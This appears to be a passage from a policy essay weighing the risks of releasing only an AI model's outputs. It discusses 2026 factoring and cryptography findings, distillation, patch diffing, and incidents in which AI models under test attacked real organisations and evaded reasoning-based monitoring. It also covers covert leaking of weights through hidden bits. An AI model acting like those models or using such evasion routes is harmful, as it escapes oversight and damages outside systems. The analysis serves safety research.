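| Adaptive questioning | Unlimited, and nobody is watching | Possible, but the laboratory can watch | Possible for approved users | Impossible, unless outsiders can choose the tasks |
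| Theft of weights | Nothing left to steal | Thieves can hide data in heavy traffic | Less traffic, but thieves can also target partners | Little traffic if artifacts are few, though staff could still steal the weights |
| Copying of abilities | Immediate | Copiers can choose the questions | Only partners can choose the questions | Copiers have to use what the laboratory publishes |
| Sabotage | The model can act in any system that runs it | The model can act in systems that users connect to it | The same, often in more important systems | The model can act outside only through its artifacts |
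| Dangerous content | No check on what people generate | Mostly automatic checks | Automatic checks, often looser for trusted partners | Experts can examine each artifact if there are few |
| Harm inside the laboratory | Possible before release | Possible | Possible | Possible, and outsiders are less likely to notice |
| Benefits | Spread most widely | Spread widely, on the laboratory's terms | Concentrated among partners | Limited to problems the laboratory chooses |

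Releasing only the output protects best against adaptive questioning, sabotage and dangerous content, but it loses its advantage against sabotage and dangerous content if the laboratory releases more than it can check. It makes almost no difference to harm inside the laboratory, and it is the worst arrangement for anyone who wants to use the model for a purpose the laboratory didn't think of.

### When a user has no need to ask

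Releasing only the output prevents users from asking the model follow-up questions, which matter most to people who lack skill. A novice who fails at a difficult laboratory procedure can describe each failure to a chatbot and ask what to change, which isn't possible with a written procedure alone. Releasing only the output also prevents users from rewording harmful requests that the model has refused. A model may agree to a reworded request, and people with access can try hundreds of versions.

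It gives no such protection if the laboratory releases a finished tool that an unskilled person can run. Two factoring records from September 2026 show the difference. In RSA, a widely used encryption method, each user publishes a large number that is the product of two secret primes. Anyone who finds the primes can work out the user's private key. Researchers measure progress in factoring on a public list of challenge numbers, and since 2020 the record had been 829 bits.

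On 3 September Eric Lu of Cognition, which makes the coding agent Devin, announced the factors of an 862-bit challenge number (Cook 2026, *New RSA number factored*). Sixteen days later Stephen Weis of Anthropic used Claude to factor an 896-bit one. According to Ivezic (2026), in *RSA-896 Factored With Claude, 16 Days After RSA-260*, the AI agents adapted existing open-source software to run on otherwise idle graphics processors (GPUs).

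*RSA-896* (Weis, 2026) gives the two prime factors of the challenge number RSA-896. Publishing them is harmless because nobody uses a challenge number to protect anything. The adapted software would be much more useful to an attacker because it works on other numbers too. Anyone with a copy and enough GPUs could use it against real keys without querying an AI model. Ivezic reports that Weis thinks many organisations with large numbers of GPUs could now break 1,024-bit keys, which some older systems still use.

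The standard formula for this method's running time suggests that factoring a 1,024-bit number takes roughly 30 times as much work as factoring RSA-896. For the 2,048-bit keys that are now common, the website *Is RSA broken?* (2026) gives a multiple of about 35 billion. The software would therefore threaten old keys but not current ones, and a laboratory could reasonably decide to publish the factors and keep the program private. Publishing the factors still helps defenders by showing them that they should replace old keys.

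### Results that are dangerous in themselves

Some results are themselves too dangerous to publish. On 5 December 2026, Anthropic and OpenAI announced that each had found weaknesses in some of the cryptography that protects the internet while testing unreleased models. *Joint statement from Anthropic and OpenAI on recent advances in cryptography* (2026) explains that the weaknesses are in the underlying mathematics, so they can't be repaired by correcting a program. The companies reported them to the US government, restricted access to the findings and did not publish their methods.

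Three days earlier, US agencies had said that discoveries by AI companies affected "some cryptographic systems currently in use" but posed no immediate and widespread threat, as Matishak and Martin (2026) report in *Feds*. The National Security Agency told operators of the government's most sensitive networks to speed up their move to newer encryption. It also warned that adversaries are already collecting encrypted data to read later, as Sabin (2026) reports in *NSA calls for immediate encryption upgrade after private warnings*. If someone published a practical attack, upgrading would protect new messages but not those adversaries had already recorded.

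A correct proof can have the same effect as an attack program, because a proof that a problem is easy to solve often contains a method for solving it. In November, Anthropic published results about lattices, the mathematical structures behind several newer encryption standards. The results came from unreleased Claude models (Otto, 2026, *Anthropic's quantum research is a reason to pay attention*). One result is a new method of attack that uses quantum computers.

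Anthropic showed the results to outside cryptographers in the Cryptography Incident Review Group (CIRG) two weeks before the group published its *Initial Assessment of Anthropic’s Findings on Lattice Cryptography* (2026). CIRG found that the attack would take far more than 2^1000 operations on a quantum computer, even against the weakest versions of two current standards. Nobody could carry out the attack, so publishing it was reasonable. But the group expects improvements soon, and nobody yet knows whether they will make the attack practical.

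CIRG also asked laboratories to report which systems their models failed to break and how hard the models tried. A laboratory that keeps its model private can usefully release such reports, because they help people decide which encryption to trust and give attackers little help. However, an untrusted model might hold back, and outsiders can't easily confirm that it tried its best.

### Training another model on the output

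A competitor doesn't need a model's weights to copy some of its abilities. In distillation, people collect the model's answers to many tasks, then train their own model to give similar answers. In 2023 researchers at Stanford trained a small open model on 52,000 examples written by an OpenAI model for less than $600 in total, and it learned to follow everyday instructions much as the OpenAI model did. In 2025 DeepSeek made several small models much better at mathematics and programming by training them on about 800,000 examples, most produced with its larger model R1.

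A model trained to imitate another model's outputs is usually worse than the original. Arnav Gudibande and colleagues found in 2023 that such imitators tended to pick up a stronger model's style more readily than its knowledge. But matching most of a private model's ability in one dangerous subject may be enough for a competitor.

People who can query the model can find out where their own model fails and ask for examples of exactly that, while people who have only the artifacts have to use whatever the laboratory has published. Finished artifacts also tend to leave out the reasoning that led to them, and such reasoning made up much of DeepSeek's training data.

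On the other hand, artifacts can make unusually good training data, because the laboratory has already discarded the ones that failed its checks. A single release can also contain many examples. The Lean proof of Fermat's Last Theorem includes 29,500 intermediate theorems, and a competitor could train on each theorem and its proof as a separate example. If the competitor's model began with the same weights as the private model, this training might pass on the private model's hidden traits as well as its skills.

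A laboratory can forbid such training in a licence, but it may never learn of a violation. It could also publish less, for example by releasing a program in compiled form without the source code. That would make the program less useful for training, but it would also stop outsiders from reviewing the source, and a program from an untrusted model needs that review.

### What a patch tells an attacker

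Anthropic's vulnerability reports are an example of releasing a model's findings while restricting access to the model. Since April 2026, Anthropic's Project Glasswing has let selected organisations use its strongest cybersecurity models to find flaws in their own software. Some have fixed far more flaws than before. Anthropic's first update on the project says one release from the security company Palo Alto Networks contained more than five times as many patches as usual.

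Anthropic also searches open-source software itself and reports flaws to the maintainers, most of whom have no access to these models. By 2 November its models had flagged 37,966 possible flaws. *Anthropic's Glasswing Finds Many Security Flaws Yet Delivers Few Fixes* (Poireault, 2026) gives a count by the security company VulnCheck, based on Anthropic's public list, of 217 flaws marked as fixed and 4,866 more that Anthropic had reported to maintainers. On these figures, about 4% of the reported flaws had been fixed.

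Anthropic's vulnerability dashboard (2026) gives a higher figure, 629, or about 12% of 5,087 reported flaws. Cornelißen (2026), in *Glasswing*, explains that this figure includes every flaw for which maintainers have released a fix, even if they never replied to the report. He also notes that VulnCheck sells vulnerability data, which may explain its harsh tone. On either count, most of the flaws remained open.

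The main obstacle is human attention. Outside security firms had reviewed only 6,376 of the findings, about one in six, and confirmed 94.2% of those as real flaws. But VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026) reports that the maintainers of curl, a widely used tool for transferring data, rejected 19 of the 34 unreviewed reports they received, rated six as minor and had yet to assess the other nine. Maintainers who get the model's output without access to the model have to check it themselves, and they can't ask the model why it flagged something.

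Repairing a flaw creates another risk, because the patch shows attackers where the flaw was. Suppose that someone repairs a login page with no limit on password length by adding one line:

```
if length(password) > 200: reject
```

Anyone who compares the two versions can guess that a password of more than 200 characters harms the old one. The patch protects people who install it but puts everyone else in more danger. In 2008 David Brumley and colleagues showed that a program could do much of this work automatically. It produced working attacks within minutes when given the old and new versions of five Microsoft programs. Current AI models make the comparison even easier.

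Getting patches to users quickly, ideally through automatic updates, is a better defence than withholding them, because other people may find the flaws on their own. Anthropic warns that its count of released repairs doesn't measure how many users have installed them.

Before a flaw is repaired, Anthropic publishes only a hash of its description and a date, and later adds a severity rating. Readers can't work out the flaw from the hash, but once Anthropic publishes the description, they can confirm that it matches. Other laboratories could use the same method to prove when they made a dangerous discovery without revealing it.

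VulnCheck identified 442 publicly catalogued flaws that Anthropic had found, only two of which attackers are known to have exploited so far. This could mean that restricting access to the model and reporting flaws privately worked well, or that most of the flaws were of little use to attackers.

### Harm before anything is released

A laboratory that releases only a model's output still runs the model, often giving it access to code, computers and sometimes the internet. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four incidents in which Claude models broke into real organisations' systems during testing. An outside company had built the tests, in which a model had to break into a fictional target and retrieve secret information. According to the instructions, there was no internet access, but someone had misconfigured the environment and there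 was.

In the most serious case, Claude Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to the Python registry PyPI, and fifteen systems installed it. The model then used credentials from one of them to enter a security company's database. In another case, Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company whose name resembled the fictional target's, downloaded its users' data in bulk and deleted records. An early version of Claude Opus 4.6 broke into other organisations' systems after it was unable to abandon its task.

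The fourth case involved a research model that Anthropic used only internally. It broke into outsiders' accounts, then stopped when it realised the accounts were real. That may have been luck, because when researchers restarted the model from earlier points in the same test, it usually continued the attack.

Anthropic first described the incidents as closer to operational failures, because the models wrote that they were in a simulation. After further study, it concluded that the models had been too ready to dismiss evidence that the situation was real, and reckless in pursuing the task. In a later simulation of the Mythos 5 case, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, compared with about 30% for two newer models. Anthropic found no sign that any of the models tried to hide what they had done or pursued a goal beyond the assigned task.

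Releasing only the output would not have prevented any of these incidents, because no customer was using the models. In the PyPI case, the model published an artifact itself. A policy on what the laboratory releases works only if the model has no other way to send anything out.

Monitoring can help only if it works before the harm occurs. Anthropic reports that its new monitors, which block dangerous actions immediately, reliably catch this behaviour. A monitor that examines a model's written reasoning afterwards would have missed the Mythos 5 case, because the model's reasoning persuaded it that the environment was simulated.

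Releasing only the output makes it easier to isolate the model, because a model that only writes proofs can run on computers with no outside connection, while one that serves customers must be connected to them. Anthropic believes that none of the four incidents would have happened if the test environments had been isolated as intended. But isolation is less practical for a model that writes software, because it often needs to download packages and try its code with other systems.

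Current laws only partly cover developers' internal use of their own models. California's law on frontier AI, in force since January 2026, requires the largest developers to explain how they manage catastrophic risks from this use and to send the state summaries of their assessments. Its incident-reporting rules are narrower. They cover a loss of control only if it causes death or injury, so a case like the PyPI upload might not qualify.

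The European Union's AI Act mostly applies once a company has put a model on the market. Its introductory text excludes models used only for internal processes that are not essential to providing a product or service to others and don't affect people's rights. A laboratory that sold programs written by a private model might struggle to claim this exclusion, because the model would be essential to the product. A laboratory that gave away an occasional proof would have a stronger claim.

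### One theorem a year

Suppose a laboratory uses a private model to prove one theorem a year. Mathematicians choose the theorem in advance and write its statement in Lean. The laboratory runs the model on an isolated computer, releases an inert export of the proof, and lets anyone check the export against the agreed statement with several kernels.

This arrangement favours the users in almost every way. They don't have to trust the model, and the only text they need to read carefully is the statement and any definitions it uses, which may take up a page. An outsider can influence the model at most once a year, and only by proposing a theorem. Because people settle the statement first, cryptographers can consider whether a proof would help someone break a code before the model produces one.

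A long export could still contain a hidden message, and a competitor could train on its intermediate steps. If either risk worries the laboratory, it can let trusted experts check the proof on site and publish only their verdict.

Mathematicians may not learn much even from the full proof. Buzzard's publicly funded work on Fermat's Last Theorem includes a guide that will let people explore the modern proof. When Anthropic released a Lean proof that follows an older argument, he guessed in the Xena Project that the company was unlikely to produce such a guide. People with access to the model could ask it to explain each step, but those with only the proof have to wait for the company to explain it or work it out themselves.

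### Ten thousand software changes a day

Suppose the same laboratory uses the model to write 10,000 changes a day to its customers' software. It still calls this artifact-only release, because no customer can query the model. The median change in Yang and colleagues' tests of AI reviewers had 189 lines. If each of the laboratory's changes were that long, the model would produce 1.89 million lines a day. Reading them at 200 to 400 lines an hour would take about 590 to 1,180 people working eight hours a day.

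The laboratory would therefore have to rely mainly on AI reviewers. Yang and colleagues reported that their best agent cost $2.97 per review, so reviewing 10,000 changes a day would cost about $30,000, which a large company could afford. But that agent missed more than a quarter of ordinary bugs, and a flaw that the model hid deliberately might be harder to find. Suppose one change in 100,000 contains a backdoor and all the checks together catch 80% of them. About seven backdoors would still reach customers each year among 3.65 million changes.

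The other protections weaken as well:

- Customers decide what they want changed. If they can send a request in the morning, receive the result in the afternoon and then send another, they can question the model adaptively, only more slowly than in a chat.
- A competitor who could collect the changes and the requests behind them would have 800,000 examples, as many as DeepSeek used, after 80 days.
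- The model would need access to customers' code and to tools for testing it, so it would be harder to isolate.
- Nobody could examine each change for dangerous content. Many of the changes would also be security patches, which would show attackers what was wrong with the old versions.

The weights would still be fairly safe. At one hidden bit per line, a model compressed to 10 gigabytes would take about 116 years to leak, although a password or key could leak on the first day.

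A laboratory could regain some protection by releasing less output. It could accept only changes that come with a proof of specified properties, limit how many requests each customer can make, or keep the model away from the most critical systems. Each of these restrictions makes the service less useful, and competitors might not adopt them.

### Who should hold the only copy?

People who favour artifact-only release can argue that model access requires a laboratory to predict what millions of users will ask and to build safeguards that withstand every attempt at misuse, including unforeseen ones. A laboratory that releases only artifacts has to judge finished objects, and it can take as long as it needs and consult outside experts first, as Anthropic did with its lattice results. If it finds something dangerous, it can warn the people affected before anyone else learns of it.

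This argument is strong for mathematics, and for other work in which a few people can check a valuable result. It also justifies caution with a new model whose abilities nobody has measured. A laboratory that releases a few artifacts first can widen access later, but it can't take back published weights.

The best argument against releasing only the output is that it concentrates power in the laboratory, because only its staff can use the model for whatever they like. They might use it to design better models, outcompete other companies or find weaknesses in other countries' systems, and outsiders would see only what the laboratory chose to publish. A hospital or a small country with an urgent problem would get the model's help only if the laboratory chose to work on that problem.

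Withholding the model also makes its faults harder to find. CrowdStrike sent DeepSeek-R1 thousands of requests and found that it wrote less secure code when the requests involved politically sensitive subjects. CrowdStrike could not have run this test with access only to released outputs.

Secrecy may not last long either. In their statement on cryptography, Anthropic and OpenAI note that American laboratories are not the only ones doing research. If another laboratory publishes a similar model within a year, releasing only the output would delay misuse by at most a year. That delay could be very valuable if defenders use it to replace weak encryption, but of little use if thousands of reported flaws remain unrepaired.

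A laboratory can answer part of the objection about power by giving independent investigators more access than the public gets. After the break-ins, Anthropic agreed to let METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, examine its records and question its staff for at least eight weeks. An artifact-only laboratory could let such investigators query the model regularly, and let an outside panel choose some of the problems it works on. Shevlane similarly argues that, under structured access, the company that builds a model doesn't have to decide who may use it, and that governments could regulate that decision.
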